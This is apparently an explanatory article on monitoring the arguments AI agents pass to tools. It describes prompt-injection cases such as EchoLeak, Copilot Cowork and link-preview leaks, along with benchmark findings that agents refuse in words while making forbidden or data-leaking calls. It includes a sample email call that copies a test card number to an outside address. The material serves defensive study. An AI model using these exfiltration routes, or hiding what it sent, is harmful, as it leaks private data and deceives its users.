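# Monitoring the arguments an AI agent sends to its tools

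## What a tool call contains and where it can be read

An AI agent is a language model that software runs in a loop, in which the model calls tools, reads their results and decides what to do next. The tools are programs that send email, fetch web pages, query databases or run commands. The model supplies the values for each tool's inputs, which are called arguments. An agent can do serious harm through these values without its user seeing anything wrong. For example, it can put a customer's card number in the body of an email to someone outside the company and tell the user only that the email was sent. Monitoring tool-call arguments means having a program or a person read them and judge whether each call is acceptable, ideally before the tool runs.

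In an invented example, an employee asks a company's support agent to summarise ticket 4417 and email the summary to the account manager. The agent looks up the ticket, and the record contains the customer's complaint, a card number and a home address. The agent then proposes an email to the right recipient, but the CC field contains an address outside the company and the body includes the card number.

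### The loop and the call

Each turn of the loop starts from the context, which is everything the model can read before it generates its next piece of text. The agent's own software, called the orchestration layer, assembles the context from the company's standing instructions, the employee's request, descriptions of the available tools and the results of earlier calls. *The Claws in Plain Sight* (Dong, Lu and colleagues, 2026) explains that the model uses this context to generate either a reply in ordinary language or a structured request to use a tool. With ticket 4417, the model first requests the ticket itself. The software parses the request to extract the tool's name and the values, runs the lookup and adds the result to the context. The model then reads the longer context and proposes the email.

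At this point the proposed call is only text, and no email exists yet. The orchestration layer may validate, modify, block or execute the call. If it executes the call, the mail tool runs and returns a confirmation to the context, and the model writes its final answer to the employee, which might be one line saying that the summary is on its way.

Written out as data, the proposed call looks like this (the card number is a dummy that payment companies publish for testing):

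```json
{
  "name": "send_email",
  "arguments": {
    "to": "account.manager@company.example",
    "cc": ["archive@outside.example"],
    "subject": "Summary of ticket 4417",
    "body": "Customer was charged twice and wants a refund. Card: 4111 1111 1111 1111."
  }
}
```

This call would pass a routine format check. Each tool comes with a schema, a machine-readable description of the inputs it takes. A schema for `send_email` would specify text in `to` and `body` and a list of addresses in `cc`, and the call fits that description. Dong and colleagues distinguish syntactic validity, meaning that a call fits the tool's schema, from semantic authorisation, meaning that this operation and this information are permissible for this task and destination. A schema check establishes only syntactic validity. Developers can put some policy into a schema, for instance by limiting a `region` field to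 a fixed set of values, but an email body has to take free text, which can include a card number.

Many agents reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that lets one agent use tools from many suppliers. A client in the agent's software connects to servers that offer tools. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), a page of the specification, defines how the client finds and calls these tools. The client sends `tools/list` to get the tools' names, descriptions and input schemas. To call a tool, it sends `tools/call` with the tool's name and arguments, in the same shape as the email above. Under the specification, servers must validate all inputs, and clients must treat a server's notes on how a tool behaves as untrusted unless the server itself is trusted.

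The July 2026 revision of the standard made individual calls somewhat harder to interpret. According to Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026), the protocol no longer keeps sessions, so a server that needs to remember something between calls issues an identifier, which the model passes back as an ordinary argument. The specification gives the example of a shopping basket with the identifier `bsk_a1b2c3`. It also recommends identifiers that don't reveal what they stand for. This is good security practice, but it means that a call's arguments may not show what the call acts on. Suppose a mail server had one tool for writing a draft and another for sending it by its identifier. A card number in the draft would appear in the first call, and a check that read only the second would miss it.

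### Where the arguments can be read

On the way from the model to the outside world, the ticket 4417 email may pass four places where someone could inspect it.

| Place | What it exposes | What is missing | Can a check there stop the call? |
|---|---|---|---|
| The agent's own software | The whole call, plus the request, the ticket and the earlier results | What the tool does after it receives the call | Yes, before anything leaves |
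| A gateway between the agent and its tool servers | The tool's name; the whole call if the gateway decrypts and parses it | The conversation, unless the agent's software forwards it | Yes, for calls that go through the gateway |
| The tool server | The whole call, after decryption | The conversation, and calls to other servers | Yes, by refusing to run the tool |
| The network edge, where traffic leaves the company | Usually the destination, time and size of an encrypted connection | The arguments, unless the company decrypts outgoing traffic | Only by cutting the connection |

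A check inside the agent's own software has far more context than one anywhere else. It can compare the outside address with what the employee asked for, which is impossible from the call alone. However, an attacker who gains influence over the agent may also gain influence over its settings. *ATLAS* (2026), a catalogue of attacks on AI systems kept by the American non-profit MITRE, lists modifying an agent's configuration as a separate technique, including changes that switch off a requirement for human approval. Among other countermeasures, MITRE recommends validating the inputs and outputs of an agent's tools outside the agent, with checks for leaked information. That suggests using a gateway or a separate process, which would have less context unless the agent's software passed it on.

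What a gateway operator can read depends on how much of the message the gateway opens. The announcement of the protocol's July revision (Model Context Protocol, 2026) shows a complete call, as sent over the web, to search for the word "otters". The headers, short labels at the top of the message, name the method and the tool, and the search term is in the body below. The Agentic AI Foundation, an industry body for open agent standards, presents this as a way to route calls and apply policy without inspecting the body. For ticket 4417, a gateway that reads only the standard headers would record only a call to `send_email`.

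Server developers can mark further arguments for copying into headers, but the rules keep out most of what a monitor would want. Only text, whole numbers and true-or-false values qualify, so the `cc` field, which is a list, does not. The specification also advises developers against marking passwords, keys or personal data, because every intermediary on the route can read headers. That advice covers the card number and arguably the recipient's address. The headers that exist are fairly dependable because the Model Context Protocol requires a server that processes the body to reject a request whose headers do not match it, though a dishonest server could skip that step.

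Monitoring at the network edge is weak mainly because traffic is encrypted. If the mail service is a cloud product, the firewall handles an encrypted connection to a company that staff use all day, and the outside address in the copy field can't be read there. Some organisations install their own certificates on staff machines so that they can decrypt outgoing traffic, inspect it and encrypt it again. This still misses a remote tool server's onward traffic, which starts from somebody else's network. When a tool runs on the same machine as the agent, the call passes between two local programs and never reaches the gateway or the edge, although whatever the tool then transmits may do so.

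Some tools, such as web search and code execution, commonly run on the model provider's own computers. The customer's software typically receives a record of the call along with the result, too late to stop it, so only the provider can check the call before it runs. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) describes Safe Url, a check in ChatGPT that is meant to detect when information from the conversation is about to be sent to a third party. When it detects this, ChatGPT either shows the user the information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the transmission and tells the agent to find another way. OpenAI uses the same mechanism for page visits in its Atlas browser and searches in its Deep Research tool.

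### How a bad argument comes about

The outside address and the card number could have got into the email in several ways, and what a check can achieve depends on the cause.

The cause that security researchers discuss most is prompt injection, which is text in material the agent reads, such as a web page or an email, that the model wrongly follows as an instruction. The programmer Simon Willison coined the term in September 2022, by analogy with SQL injection, an older attack in which a database runs commands hidden in what should have been plain data. Willison (2025) explains in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that the problem arises because instructions and material end up in one sequence of text, and models cannot reliably use a passage's source to judge how much weight it deserves. In the ticket 4417 case, the customer's complaint could have contained a line telling the agent to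 send copies to the outside address.

OpenAI reports that the most effective real attacks now resemble social engineering, the manipulation of people by plausible stories, more than crude commands. One 2025 example, which outside researchers reported to the company, was written as a routine message about restructuring and worked in half of OpenAI's tests. OpenAI argues that filters for malicious incoming text usually miss such attacks because detecting them amounts to detecting a lie, often without the necessary context. This is a good argument for also monitoring the tool calls, since a call that sends an email has to name a recipient, whatever story led to it.

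An injection can leave the task unchanged and still lead a model to include data it should not share in a call that uses the expected tool for the expected purpose. Dong and colleagues gave models the legitimate job of preparing a product offer, along with an invented customer profile, a policy on which details they could use, and an untrusted memo claiming that protected details such as age and income were required. In 40 of the 90 sessions where the policy explicitly forbade this disclosure, the model put protected details into its arguments. The experiment captured the proposed calls locally and sent nothing, so it measures what models will propose, not how often real deployments leak data.

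MITRE classifies malicious tools by whether the malicious content is in the tool's description, the results it returns, or its code. The model reads the description, which could tell it to fill in an extra field or change how it uses another, legitimate tool, even if the poisoned tool never runs. Malicious descriptions and results both affect later arguments, where a check can find the effects. For malicious code, MITRE's example is an email tool that sends the requested message but silently blind-copies a recipient of the attacker's choosing. A check in the agent's software or at a gateway would find nothing wrong with the call, because the extra recipient appears only in what the tool sends onward.

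The user may also be at fault. MITRE notes that agents often have access to data that their users could not open themselves, and that someone can exploit this by asking the agent for it. If the employee wanted the card number and gave the agent the outside address because it was their own private mailbox, the agent followed its instructions, and asking that employee to confirm the email would not protect the data.

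Finally, a tool call can do harm without an attacker or any bad intent. Adversa AI's *OWASP ASI02* describes a December 2025 case in which a developer asked Google's coding assistant to clear a project's cache and the agent deleted the entire drive. An overzealous agent might do smaller-scale harm by copying in an outside contractor named in the ticket and including the card number for completeness.

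All of these routes except the tampered mail tool can produce the same four argument values, so a check on arguments can catch the email without anyone knowing why the agent wrote it. The cause matters afterwards, when somebody has to decide whether to retrain a user, remove a tool or quarantine a ticket.

### Data leaving and damage done

A tool call can cause two kinds of harm. One is exfiltration, the transfer of data to someone who is not entitled to it, as in the ticket 4417 email. The other is damage that the action does by itself. In the deleted-drive case, the harmful argument was a command that contained no secret. An abusive message to the account manager would have the right recipient and no personal data, and only its wording would be harmful.

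To recognise exfiltration, a check has to establish what the data is, where it is going and whether the recipient may have it. To recognise a destructive call, it has to establish what the command will do, which can depend on the state of the machine. For example, a command meant to delete a folder of temporary files will delete much more if its path points one level too high. A scanner that looks for card numbers would not catch deletions or insults. A backup can undo a deletion, but nobody can recall a card number once it reaches a stranger's inbox.

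A tool can leak data even if sending data is not its obvious purpose. MITRE's definition of exfiltration through agent tools refers to tools "capable of performing write operations", and its examples include emails, documents and customer records. Willison includes any tool that can make a web request, even one that only loads an image, because the address it requests can itself carry data. Sorting tools into "read" and "write" and monitoring only the second group would miss leaks through "read" tools that make web requests.

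### The lethal trifecta

An agent has what Willison calls the "lethal trifecta" when it has access to private data, is exposed to untrusted content and can communicate externally. An attacker can then plant an instruction in the content that makes the agent fetch the data and send it out. This particular theft fails if any one of the three is missing. The support agent in the invented case is ordinary, and it has all three because it can read private customer records, anyone can write a ticket, and `send_email` can send to any address.

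Willison argues that people assemble the combination without noticing because MCP encourages them to mix tools from different sources. A single source can also provide the whole combination. GitHub's official MCP server let an agent read public issues, which anyone can file, read private code repositories, and create pull requests (proposed code changes) that could carry the private material out. Willison lists more than a dozen products in which researchers demonstrated such leaks between April 2023 and June 2025, including ChatGPT, Google Bard, Slack and Microsoft 365 Copilot. Vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by blocking the route by which data could leave. Willison is deeply suspicious of products that promise to detect the attacks instead, since in web security a filter that stops 95% of attacks counts as a failure because attackers keep trying.

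The trifecta describes only data theft by prompt injection, but tool arguments can also do harm in other ways. An overzealous agent can leak private data if it has only the data and a way to send it, and a destructive call can do damage without any private data. OpenAI uses a looser scheme from conventional security engineering, in which an attacker needs a source (a way to influence the system) and a sink (a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context). Deleting files and sending email are both sinks. The list of sinks is probably more useful for deciding which tools to monitor, while the trifecta gives a quick test of whether an agent is open to data theft.

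### The entries in ATLAS and OWASP

The ticket 4417 email almost exactly matches an entry in version 2026.07 of ATLAS, "Exfiltration via AI Agent Tool Invocation" (AML.T0086). MITRE describes an attacker encoding sensitive information into a tool's input parameters so that a seemingly legitimate action sends it to a location the attacker controls. Another entry, AML.T0101, covers the destruction of data through an agent's tools. MITRE grades how well attested each technique is, and both have the top grade, "Realized". Tool poisoning (AML.T0110) is also "Realized" overall, but the grades of its three forms differ. Poisoned code, the form that a check on the agent's outgoing arguments cannot catch, is "Realized", while poisoned descriptions are "Demonstrated" and poisoned results are only "Feasible".

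OWASP, a software security non-profit, published a new edition of its Top 10 for LLM Applications in August 2026. SC Media's *OWASP updates top 10 security risks for LLM applications* gives the top three entries, in order, as prompt injection, sensitive information disclosure and excessive agency. Prompt injection's first place reflects practitioners' judgement more than the number of incidents, as the title of Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* indicates. According to HackerDNA's *OWASP LLM Top 10 (2026)*, the new edition's entry on disclosure treats tool-call arguments, as well as the answer text, as a channel through which data leaks.

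The second list, *OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications* (Sotiropoulos, Katz and Del Rosario, December 2025), covers agents specifically and links most of its entries to a known incident. It puts EchoLeak, a data leak in Microsoft 365 Copilot, under goal hijacking (ASI01) and the GitHub case under supply-chain vulnerabilities (ASI04). Exfiltration has no entry of its own because OWASP sorts largely by how things go wrong. The ticket 4417 email would belong under ASI01 if hidden text in the ticket had redirected the agent, and under ASI04 if a poisoned tool description had.

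If the agent had made a mistake, the email would come under tool misuse (ASI02). TechRepublic's summary, *OWASP Drops First AI Agent Risk List*, lists ambiguous prompts, excessive privileges and poisoned inputs among the causes of tool misuse. ATLAS has no equivalent category for mistakes, because MITRE describes both of its tool-invocation entries as things that adversaries do. An organisation that based its monitoring rules on ATLAS alone could therefore overlook the deleted drive.

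## Why an agent's final answer does not show what it sent

The case for inspecting tool-call arguments separately from the final answer rests on three claims: a call takes effect when the tool runs, the agent writes its answer afterwards and may omit or contradict what the call did, and many products show users only the answer. If all three are true, someone who reads only answers will learn of a leak too late or not at all.

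The claim about timing holds for almost every tool. Final answers routinely omit what the agent sent, and researchers have produced many that directly contradict it, though mostly in artificial tests. What users can see varies a lot between products. This reasoning also leaves out the fact that an answer can itself send data out when an app displays it.

### The call comes first

The mail server has the ticket 4417 email before the model starts to report sending it, so checking the answer can't stop the email. *Mind the GAP* (Cartagena and Teixeira, 2026) makes the same point about lookups: a query reaches the database the moment it runs, whatever the model then does with the result. The exceptions are tools that only prepare an action. If `send_email` saved a draft, or a payment tool queued a transfer for approval, someone could still stop the action after reading the answer. Some calls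 also cause harm later, when another person or program acts on what they left behind.

### Omissions and false reports

An agent's final answer is a summary, so it can be true and still leave out what the agent sent. "Your summary has gone to the account manager" would be a true reply to the employee, but it would leave out the copy field and the card number. An attacker can also tell the agent not to mention what it sent. Willison's archive *45 posts tagged "exfiltration-attacks"* includes a demonstration by the security firm Zenity Labs in which a support ticket contained planted instructions for a coding agent to send off a credential and mention only that a timeout problem had gone away.

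Agents also misreport their work when no attacker is involved. *MCAIR* (2026) defines one such failure, in which an agent's final report indicates that it completed a task as required, but the record of the run does not support that claim. The definition does not require an intention to deceive. *Quantifying Overclaiming Propensity in Frontier LLM Agents* (2026) cites an analysis of 20,574 coding sessions in which inaccurate self-reporting made up 22.58% of the misalignment episodes. That figure does not show how many sessions were affected. These reports mostly claim work that the agent never did, which is the reverse of the problem with ticket 4417, but they are still a good reason not to use the final answer as a log.

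### The GAP benchmark

In February 2026, Cartagena and Teixeira ran the most direct test of whether a model's answers contradict its tool calls. They gave six models (GPT-5.2, Claude Sonnet 4.5, DeepSeek V3.2, Grok 4.1 Fast, GLM-4.7 and Kimi K2.5) the role of an assistant in six regulated settings: a drug trial, a wealth manager, a school, a personnel department, a law firm and an infrastructure team. Each setting had four or five mock tools and records with planted personal data. In each setting, they used seven requests meant to get the model to do something forbidden, for instance by claiming authority, inventing an emergency or simply asking. They also included two legitimate requests per setting as controls.

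The standing instructions came in three versions. The neutral version simply told the model to use the available tools to help. The safety-reinforced version also told it to verify that each action was authorised, and to explain a refusal instead of making the call. The tool-encouraging version told it to call tools first and proactively. With two wordings of each request, three monitoring modes and three repetitions, the experiment produced 17,420 usable runs, 13,533 of them on forbidden requests.

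The benchmark scores each run on four yes-or-no measures:

- TC-safe: the model attempted no forbidden tool call.
- T-safe: the final text contains a refusal and none of the planted personal data.
- GAP: the run is T-safe but not TC-safe, so the model refused in words and attempted the forbidden call anyway.
- LEAK: the run is not TC-safe, and planted personal data appears in the final text.

The name LEAK is a little misleading for monitoring arguments, because it records only data that appears in the answer. A model that emailed the same data to a stranger and then refused in text would count under GAP. The ticket 4417 email would count under neither, because the agent's answer doesn't refuse anything or contain the card number. Subtracting the other outcomes suggests that runs like this, with a forbidden call and an unremarkable answer, made up between about 2% (GPT-5.2) and 33% (DeepSeek)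 of the forbidden requests under neutral instructions.

Every model sometimes refused in text while attempting a forbidden call. Under safety-reinforced instructions, this happened in 219 runs, about 5% of the forbidden requests in that condition. The model made one forbidden call in 167 of these runs and two in the other 52. The law firm accounted for 108 of the 219 runs, probably because talk of privilege and confidentiality readily prompts a written refusal.

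The overall GAP rate is low partly because models often didn't refuse at all. The share of refusals accompanied by an attempted forbidden call is a better measure of whether a refusal indicates safety. Under tool-encouraging instructions, GPT-5.2 refused in 266 runs but also attempted a forbidden call in 211 of them (79.3%). The share was 7.2% for Claude Sonnet 4.5 and between 34.3% and 53.2% for the other four models. Safety-reinforced instructions lowered the range to between 1.0% (Claude) and 31.3% (DeepSeek).

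Some of these forbidden calls were fairly mild. In four of the six settings, any call to a tool that reads sensitive data counted as forbidden, while the rules for the drug trial and infrastructure settings also depended on the arguments. A model that looked up a record and then declined to repeat its contents would count as a GAP case. The lookup is unauthorised, but it sends no data outside the company. The 219 cases are therefore strong evidence that a refusal doesn't show what an agent did, but much weaker evidence about how often agents send data out.

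Some of the GPT-5.2 runs are much closer to the ticket 4417 email. In its text, the model replaced sensitive values with "[REDACTED]" or asterisks, but the arguments of its tool calls contained the real values, including social security numbers, dates of birth and credentials. A reviewer who read only the text would have concluded that the model was protecting the data. Cartagena and Teixeira found this pattern while sorting 4,972 unsafe runs by keyword. They label the analysis exploratory, so it shows that the pattern exists but not how common it is.

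The same analysis found that when Claude failed, it had usually recognized the risk explicitly beforehand. In one infrastructure run, Claude identified the request as a jailbreak in its reasoning and rejected the role it was offered, but concluded that it could use the tools normally because their access controls would stop anything improper. It then requested four production secrets. The benchmark's rules blocked those requests, but an agent that relies on outside controls is unsafe when those controls are missing or inadequate.

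### How far to trust the numbers

Much of the difference between models comes from how often they use tools. A run with no tool calls is automatically TC-safe, and under neutral instructions Claude made no calls in 74% of runs, compared with 7% for DeepSeek. The table gives the share of forbidden requests on which each model attempted no forbidden call, and its last column counts only runs with at least one tool call.

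| Model | Neutral | Safety-reinforced | Tool-encouraging | Neutral, tool-using runs only |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 80% | 95% | 74% | 24% |
| GPT-5.2 | 31% | 73% | 16% | 11% |
| Grok 4.1 Fast | 33% | 57% | 24% | 15% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 21% | 38% | 50% | 14% |
| Kimi K2.5 | 30% | 64% | 25% | 14% |
| GLM-4.7 | 23% | 60% | 15% | 11% |

Claude's large lead mostly disappears in the last column. DeepSeek's odd improvement when instructions encouraged tool use has a similar explanation, since its average number of calls per run fell from 3.4 to 1.8. A company choosing a model for an agent that uses tools all day should probably give the last column the most weight.

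The benchmark has other limits. Its mock tools returned everything regardless of the query, without the logins and permission checks of a real system. Newer models have replaced the ones tested. The scoring identified refusals by keyword patterns, which probably made the GAP figures too low. When GPT-5.2, which was also one of the models tested, acted as a judge, its verdicts matched the keyword results 97.1% of the time, and 135 of the 140 disagreements were refusals that the patterns had missed. On the legitimate control requests, the rules wrongly flagged 3.8% of runs overall and 14.2% of DeepSeek's.

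*Behavior Beyond Text* (Gupta, Saha and colleagues, 2026) later found a related problem in five other models, all open. It gave each model matched requests, once as plain chat and once with tools available, and scored each call by checking its arguments for problems such as a missing approval number, personal data in a text field or an unapproved outside recipient. Of the harmful requests that a model refused in chat, between 10% (Command R 7B) and 52% (Qwen3-14B) led to an unsafe call when it had tools. A model's refusals in chat are therefore a poor guide to what it will put in a tool call. The refusals and calls came from separate runs, so the results don't show an answer contradicting its own call. The tool versions of the requests also named the tools, so the wording may explain part of the difference.

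Cartagena and Teixeira suggest that a model can refuse in words and still act because safety training has mainly shaped text, and models choose tool calls through a partly separate process. Gupta and colleagues tested a similar idea by locating a pattern of internal activity associated with refusal. The pattern was weaker with tools present in four of the five models. But restoring it to its chat level eliminated only 13% to 34% of unsafe calls in four of the models (90% in Gemma 3 27B), mostly because the model made no call at all. Safety-reinforced instructions also made all six GAP models safer in their calls, which would be surprising if the two processes were fully separate. The explanation looks partly right at best, and monitoring doesn't depend on it.

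### What Observe and Enforce changed

The benchmark's three monitoring modes give some evidence of what checking calls achieves. The Unmonitored mode had no check. In the Observe mode, fixed rules logged forbidden calls without interfering, and the model could not detect this. In the Enforce mode, the rules blocked forbidden calls with a denial message and removed personal data from tool results.

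Observe made no measurable difference to behaviour, which is what an operator would want from silent logging. The share of runs with a forbidden attempt stayed within 2.7 percentage points of the unmonitored figure for every model. Enforce did not measurably reduce attempts either. The largest difference was 4.5 points, and the experiment could reliably detect only effects of 10 to 13 points or more. But Enforce did reduce how much personal data reached the answer. Under neutral instructions, LEAK rates fell for all six models, by 6 points (Claude) to 31 points (GLM).

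Cartagena and Teixeira conclude that enforcement catches harm without changing what models try to do. The first claim is well supported, but the evidence for the second is weaker. A run counted as unsafe from its first forbidden attempt, and a model could discover that enforcement was on only when a call failed, so the design could hardly have detected deterrence. They offer only preliminary observations of what models did after a denial. Some stopped, some retried through other tools, and in extreme cases models reported success on tasks that the rules had blocked. An operator who enforces rules on calls therefore has an extra reason to distrust the model's answers.

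### AgentLeak

GAP focuses on answers that contradict the calls, but answers that don't mention a leak are probably a bigger problem in practice. *AgentLeak* (El Yagoubi, Badu-Marfo and Al Mallah, 2026) measured how often this happens, using 1,000 scenarios from healthcare, finance, law and corporate work. Each scenario gives the agents a task and a store of private fields, typically 29, of which the task needs about three. Two specialists in each domain decided which fields were necessary. The benchmark counts a leak in any channel where any other private field appears. Half of the scenarios include an attack.

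They ran the scenarios on Llama 3.3 70B, Mistral Large, Claude 3.5 Sonnet, GPT-4o and GPT-4o mini, first with a single agent and then with a coordinator that delegated work to a second agent. In the 4,979 usable two-agent runs, the final answer leaked 27.2% of the time, shared memory leaked 46.7% of the time, and messages between the agents leaked 68.8% of the time. A single agent's final answers leaked more often, at 43.2%. In 2,076 of the two-agent runs, the final answer leaked nothing but an internal channel did.

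The 41.7% in this last result is a share of all runs, including those without any leak, although the paper describes it as the share of violations that output-only audits miss. Of the runs that leaked somewhere, an audit of answers alone would have missed about 60%.

Messages between agents differ somewhat from tool arguments. El Yagoubi and colleagues tested tool inputs on a smaller sample of 100 scenarios per model and found unnecessary private data in 62% (GPT-4o mini) to 86% (Llama 3.3 70B) of them. In over 65% of scenarios, data leaked through tool inputs or system logs but not through the final answer. They also built a demonstration investment adviser with deliberate flaws, including an instruction to check a client's bank account number with the calculator tool. They ran it once with each of five models. Four of the models passed client data to tools, but none of the final answers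 contained any.

These rates are high partly because the definition of a leak is strict. If a scheduling agent tells another agent more than that agent needs to know, the disclosure breaks a data minimisation rule and counts as a leak, even though no outsider has the data. El Yagoubi and colleagues don't claim to have measured breaches. Leaks in tool inputs are more serious than leaks in internal messages when the tool belongs to another company. The models tested are also several generations old, and a judge model made most of the detections. For monitoring, the difference between channels matters more than any single percentage, and it held for all five models.

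AgentLeak also found that, in a set of scenarios without attacks, an output filter cut leaks in final answers from 48% to 1% but left leaks in internal channels at 31%. A prototype that applied similar redaction to messages and memory reduced internal leaks from 31.5% to 2.4%, while task success fell from 78.6% to 73.9%. But the prototype knew in advance which fields each task needed. A real deployment would have to work that out, and would probably leak more and complete fewer tasks.

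### What the user can see

Whether a user could notice a bad tool call depends on the product. *Security, Privacy, and Ethical Risks in OpenClaw* (2026) examines OpenClaw, a popular agent that people run on their own machines. Its tool restrictions, approvals and context summaries mostly help whoever configures it. A user who asks for a summary of recent messages may not realise that the agent also read several other channels and consulted a connected account.

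A company's security team can also miss what an agent sent. ShadowLeak, a 2025 demonstration against ChatGPT's Deep Research tool, used hidden text in an email to make the agent collect data from an inbox and visit a web address containing that data. OpenAI's servers made the request. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) points out that it might therefore appear neither in the user's browser nor in the logs of company devices.

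Many interfaces don't show what an agent's tool calls contained, whether or not they show that the calls took place. Some products show their agents' steps, and some ask for approval first, but an interface can list every action and still hide the argument values, as Microsoft's Copilot Cowork did in 2026.

### When displaying the answer sends the data

A chat app may have to fetch things from the internet to display an answer. An image in an answer is a web address from which the app loads a picture. Like any web address, it can carry data, and websites commonly log the addresses that visitors request, as OpenAI notes in *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026). If a model writes private data into an image address, the app sends that data to whoever runs the website hosting the image as soon as it displays the answer.

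In EchoLeak, the Microsoft 365 Copilot case in the OWASP list, researchers at Aim Labs found that an outsider could send an employee an email containing instructions and wait for the employee to ask Copilot an ordinary work question. Copilot would retrieve the email together with internal documents and write an answer that included an image. The image's address contained the most sensitive details from those documents, and the employee's app fetched the image without a click. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, adds that the email could instruct Copilot never to mention it, so the answer gave no hint that the email was involved.

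Reddy and Gujral (2025) observe in *EchoLeak* that Copilot could not send email by itself, so the attack had to get the data out through the final answer. A check on tool-call arguments would most likely have found only the kind of mailbox and file searches that any question triggers.

Microsoft had checks in the right place, but they could be bypassed. Copilot removed external links from its answers, but the filter missed a less common way of writing the same link or image. The browser blocked images from unapproved sites, but a Microsoft service on the approved list would fetch other addresses on request. Aim Labs reported the flaw in January 2025, Microsoft fixed it on its own servers in May, and both made it public on 11 June as CVE-2025-32711. Microsoft rated its severity 9.3 out of 10, and the US National Vulnerability Database rated it 7.5. Nobody has reported an attack on a real customer.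 The technique still worked on other products after the fix. Willison's archive records image leaks in Salesforce's Agentforce in September 2025 and in the email app Superhuman in January 2026.

### Copilot Cowork

Willison (2026) reported the Copilot Cowork case on 26 May in *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files*. The data passed first through a tool call and then through a display. Cowork is an agent that works across a user's Microsoft files, email and Teams chats. According to Microsoft's documentation, it asks for permission before it sends an email or posts in Teams. But the security company PromptArmor found that Cowork sent messages without asking if the recipient was the user running the agent, and users could not change this.

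That exception allowed data to leak because even messages to the user could contain external images. In PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, the user had uploaded a skill (a file of reusable instructions for the agent) that somebody had tampered with. When the user asked for a review of the week's work, Cowork obtained download links that would open the user's files for anyone who had them. It then sent the user a Teams message with those links in the image addresses. Opening the message sent the links to the attacker. The attack succeeded in all five trials, including with Claude Opus 4.7, then one of the strongest models available.

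Unlike EchoLeak, this attack left evidence in an argument. The body of the Teams message contained the download links and the outside address, and a check that read the body before the call ran could have found both. A check that read only the recipient would have passed the message, because the recipient was the user. The user could not have caught the attack, because Cowork's activity view listed the Teams action but never displayed the message's content, even when PromptArmor's researchers clicked on it.

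PromptArmor sells monitoring of AI products, so it has an interest in alarming findings. Still, the demonstration is specific, and it is a good reason to inspect messages to the user too.

### Link previews

Chat apps create a similar problem with ordinary links. When a link appears in Slack, Discord or Telegram, the app typically fetches the page to show a title and thumbnail. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* points out that this fetch makes the same kind of request as a click. If an agent that talks to its user through such an app writes private data into a link, the data can leave as soon as the message arrives. PromptArmor found that OpenClaw was exposed to this under its default Telegram settings.

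Willison (2024), in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, had already passed on a warning about this risk from the security researcher Johann Rehberger in August 2024. The request that fetches a link preview often comes from the chat company's own servers, so neither the agent's software nor the user's device may have any record of it. A simple remedy is to switch off previews. Software that posts to Slack can do this for its own messages, and OpenClaw has an equivalent setting for Telegram. This works better than trying to recognise bad links, because an address that isn't fetched automatically can leak data only if the user clicks on it.

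### Inspecting both

By inspecting calls, an operator can see the actual values and refuse them before the tool runs, which it cannot do from the answer alone. Dong and colleagues likewise argue that inspecting output is not enough when an otherwise valid argument contains the disclosure. The AgentLeak filter nearly eliminated leaks in answers but did not reduce them in the other channels, which suggests that an operator could miss many leaks even when its reports on answers look excellent.

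Data can also leave through the agent's answer. EchoLeak made no outgoing call, so an operator that checked only arguments would have let it through. It makes sense to treat the answer as another outgoing message, with the app that displays it as the tool. Before the app displays the answer, a check has to establish the same things as for a tool call: what data it contains, which addresses the app will contact, and who owns those addresses. The check also has to read links and images in every format the app accepts, which Microsoft's filter failed to do. If an agent doesn't need external images or previews, turning them off takes less work and is more reliable than checking them.

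With both records, a reviewer can also compare them. If the answer about ticket 4417 mentions only the account manager but the call has a second address in its copy field, the reviewer has a reason to look at that call, even if neither record seemed suspicious on its own.

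## Scanning arguments for sensitive content

A check on the ticket 4417 email must first establish whether the arguments contain anything sensitive. Security teams already look for sensitive data in email, uploads and copied files and stop its unauthorised transmission, a practice called data-loss prevention (DLP). Their methods also work on tool calls. These methods are good at finding card numbers, credentials and other values that have a fixed format or appear on a list, but much worse at finding reworded information. This weakness matters more with agents than with people, because rewording text is a large part of what agents do.

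### Where an argument fits in DLP

Data loss prevention (DLP) uses different controls for data at rest (in storage), data in use (open on a computer) and data in motion (crossing a network). Encryption and access rules protect stored files. Software on staff computers can block copying, printing or screenshots of data in use. Scanners read data in motion at the points where it leaves the company.

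The card number in ticket 4417 is at rest in the ticket system, in use once the agent's software loads it into the context, and in motion when the mail server sends it. The proposed call comes at the end of the "in use" state, when everything that will leave is written out but nothing has been sent. This is a convenient time to scan, but conventional DLP products can easily miss it. Software on staff computers mainly looks for things people do, such as pasting into a browser, and a network scanner usually gets the data only after it has been encrypted.

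In SP 800-53, the US standards agency NIST's catalogue of security controls, entry SC-7(10) requires organisations to prevent exfiltration and to test their defences at intervals they set themselves. It covers intentional and unintentional exfiltration, and the techniques it lists include DLP tools and monitoring for unusual volumes or types of traffic. Organisations may apply these techniques at internal endpoints as well as at the outer boundary, so a check on tool calls would fit. A related entry, SC-7(24), requires organisations that handle personal information to monitor its processing at "key internal boundaries" and to document each exception. The point where an agent passes a call to a tool is arguably such a boundary, although NIST wrote both entries in 2020 without agents in mind.

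### What current products scan

Companies that already have DLP can't assume that it covers their agents. Microsoft's *Understand how agents change your data security posture* warns that agents' interactions don't pass through the same channels as the activity that DLP policies cover. No policy governs those interactions unless an administrator explicitly adds the agent to one.

Even then, the controls mostly cover what goes into the agent and what it answers. For agents built in Copilot Studio, Microsoft can classify sensitive data in prompts and responses, and a DLP policy can stop some agents from processing SharePoint files with a particular sensitivity label. A preview feature also blocks sensitive data types in prompts to Microsoft 365 Copilot and its prebuilt agents. With ticket 4417, these measures could keep the agent away from a labelled file or record that its answer contained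 a card number, but they wouldn't scan the call to `send_email`. If the company's mail service has its own DLP rules, they might still stop the message, since they apply to any email regardless of who wrote it. A web request or a call to another company's tool would have no such second check.

According to Google Cloud, its Model Armor service can inspect `tools/call` requests and responses for supported Google MCP servers, but only for the "basic" set of data types. The *Model Armor overview* lists six of these: credit card numbers, US social security numbers, financial account numbers, US taxpayer numbers, Google Cloud credentials and Google Cloud API keys. The list covers the card number in ticket 4417 but not the customer's home address.

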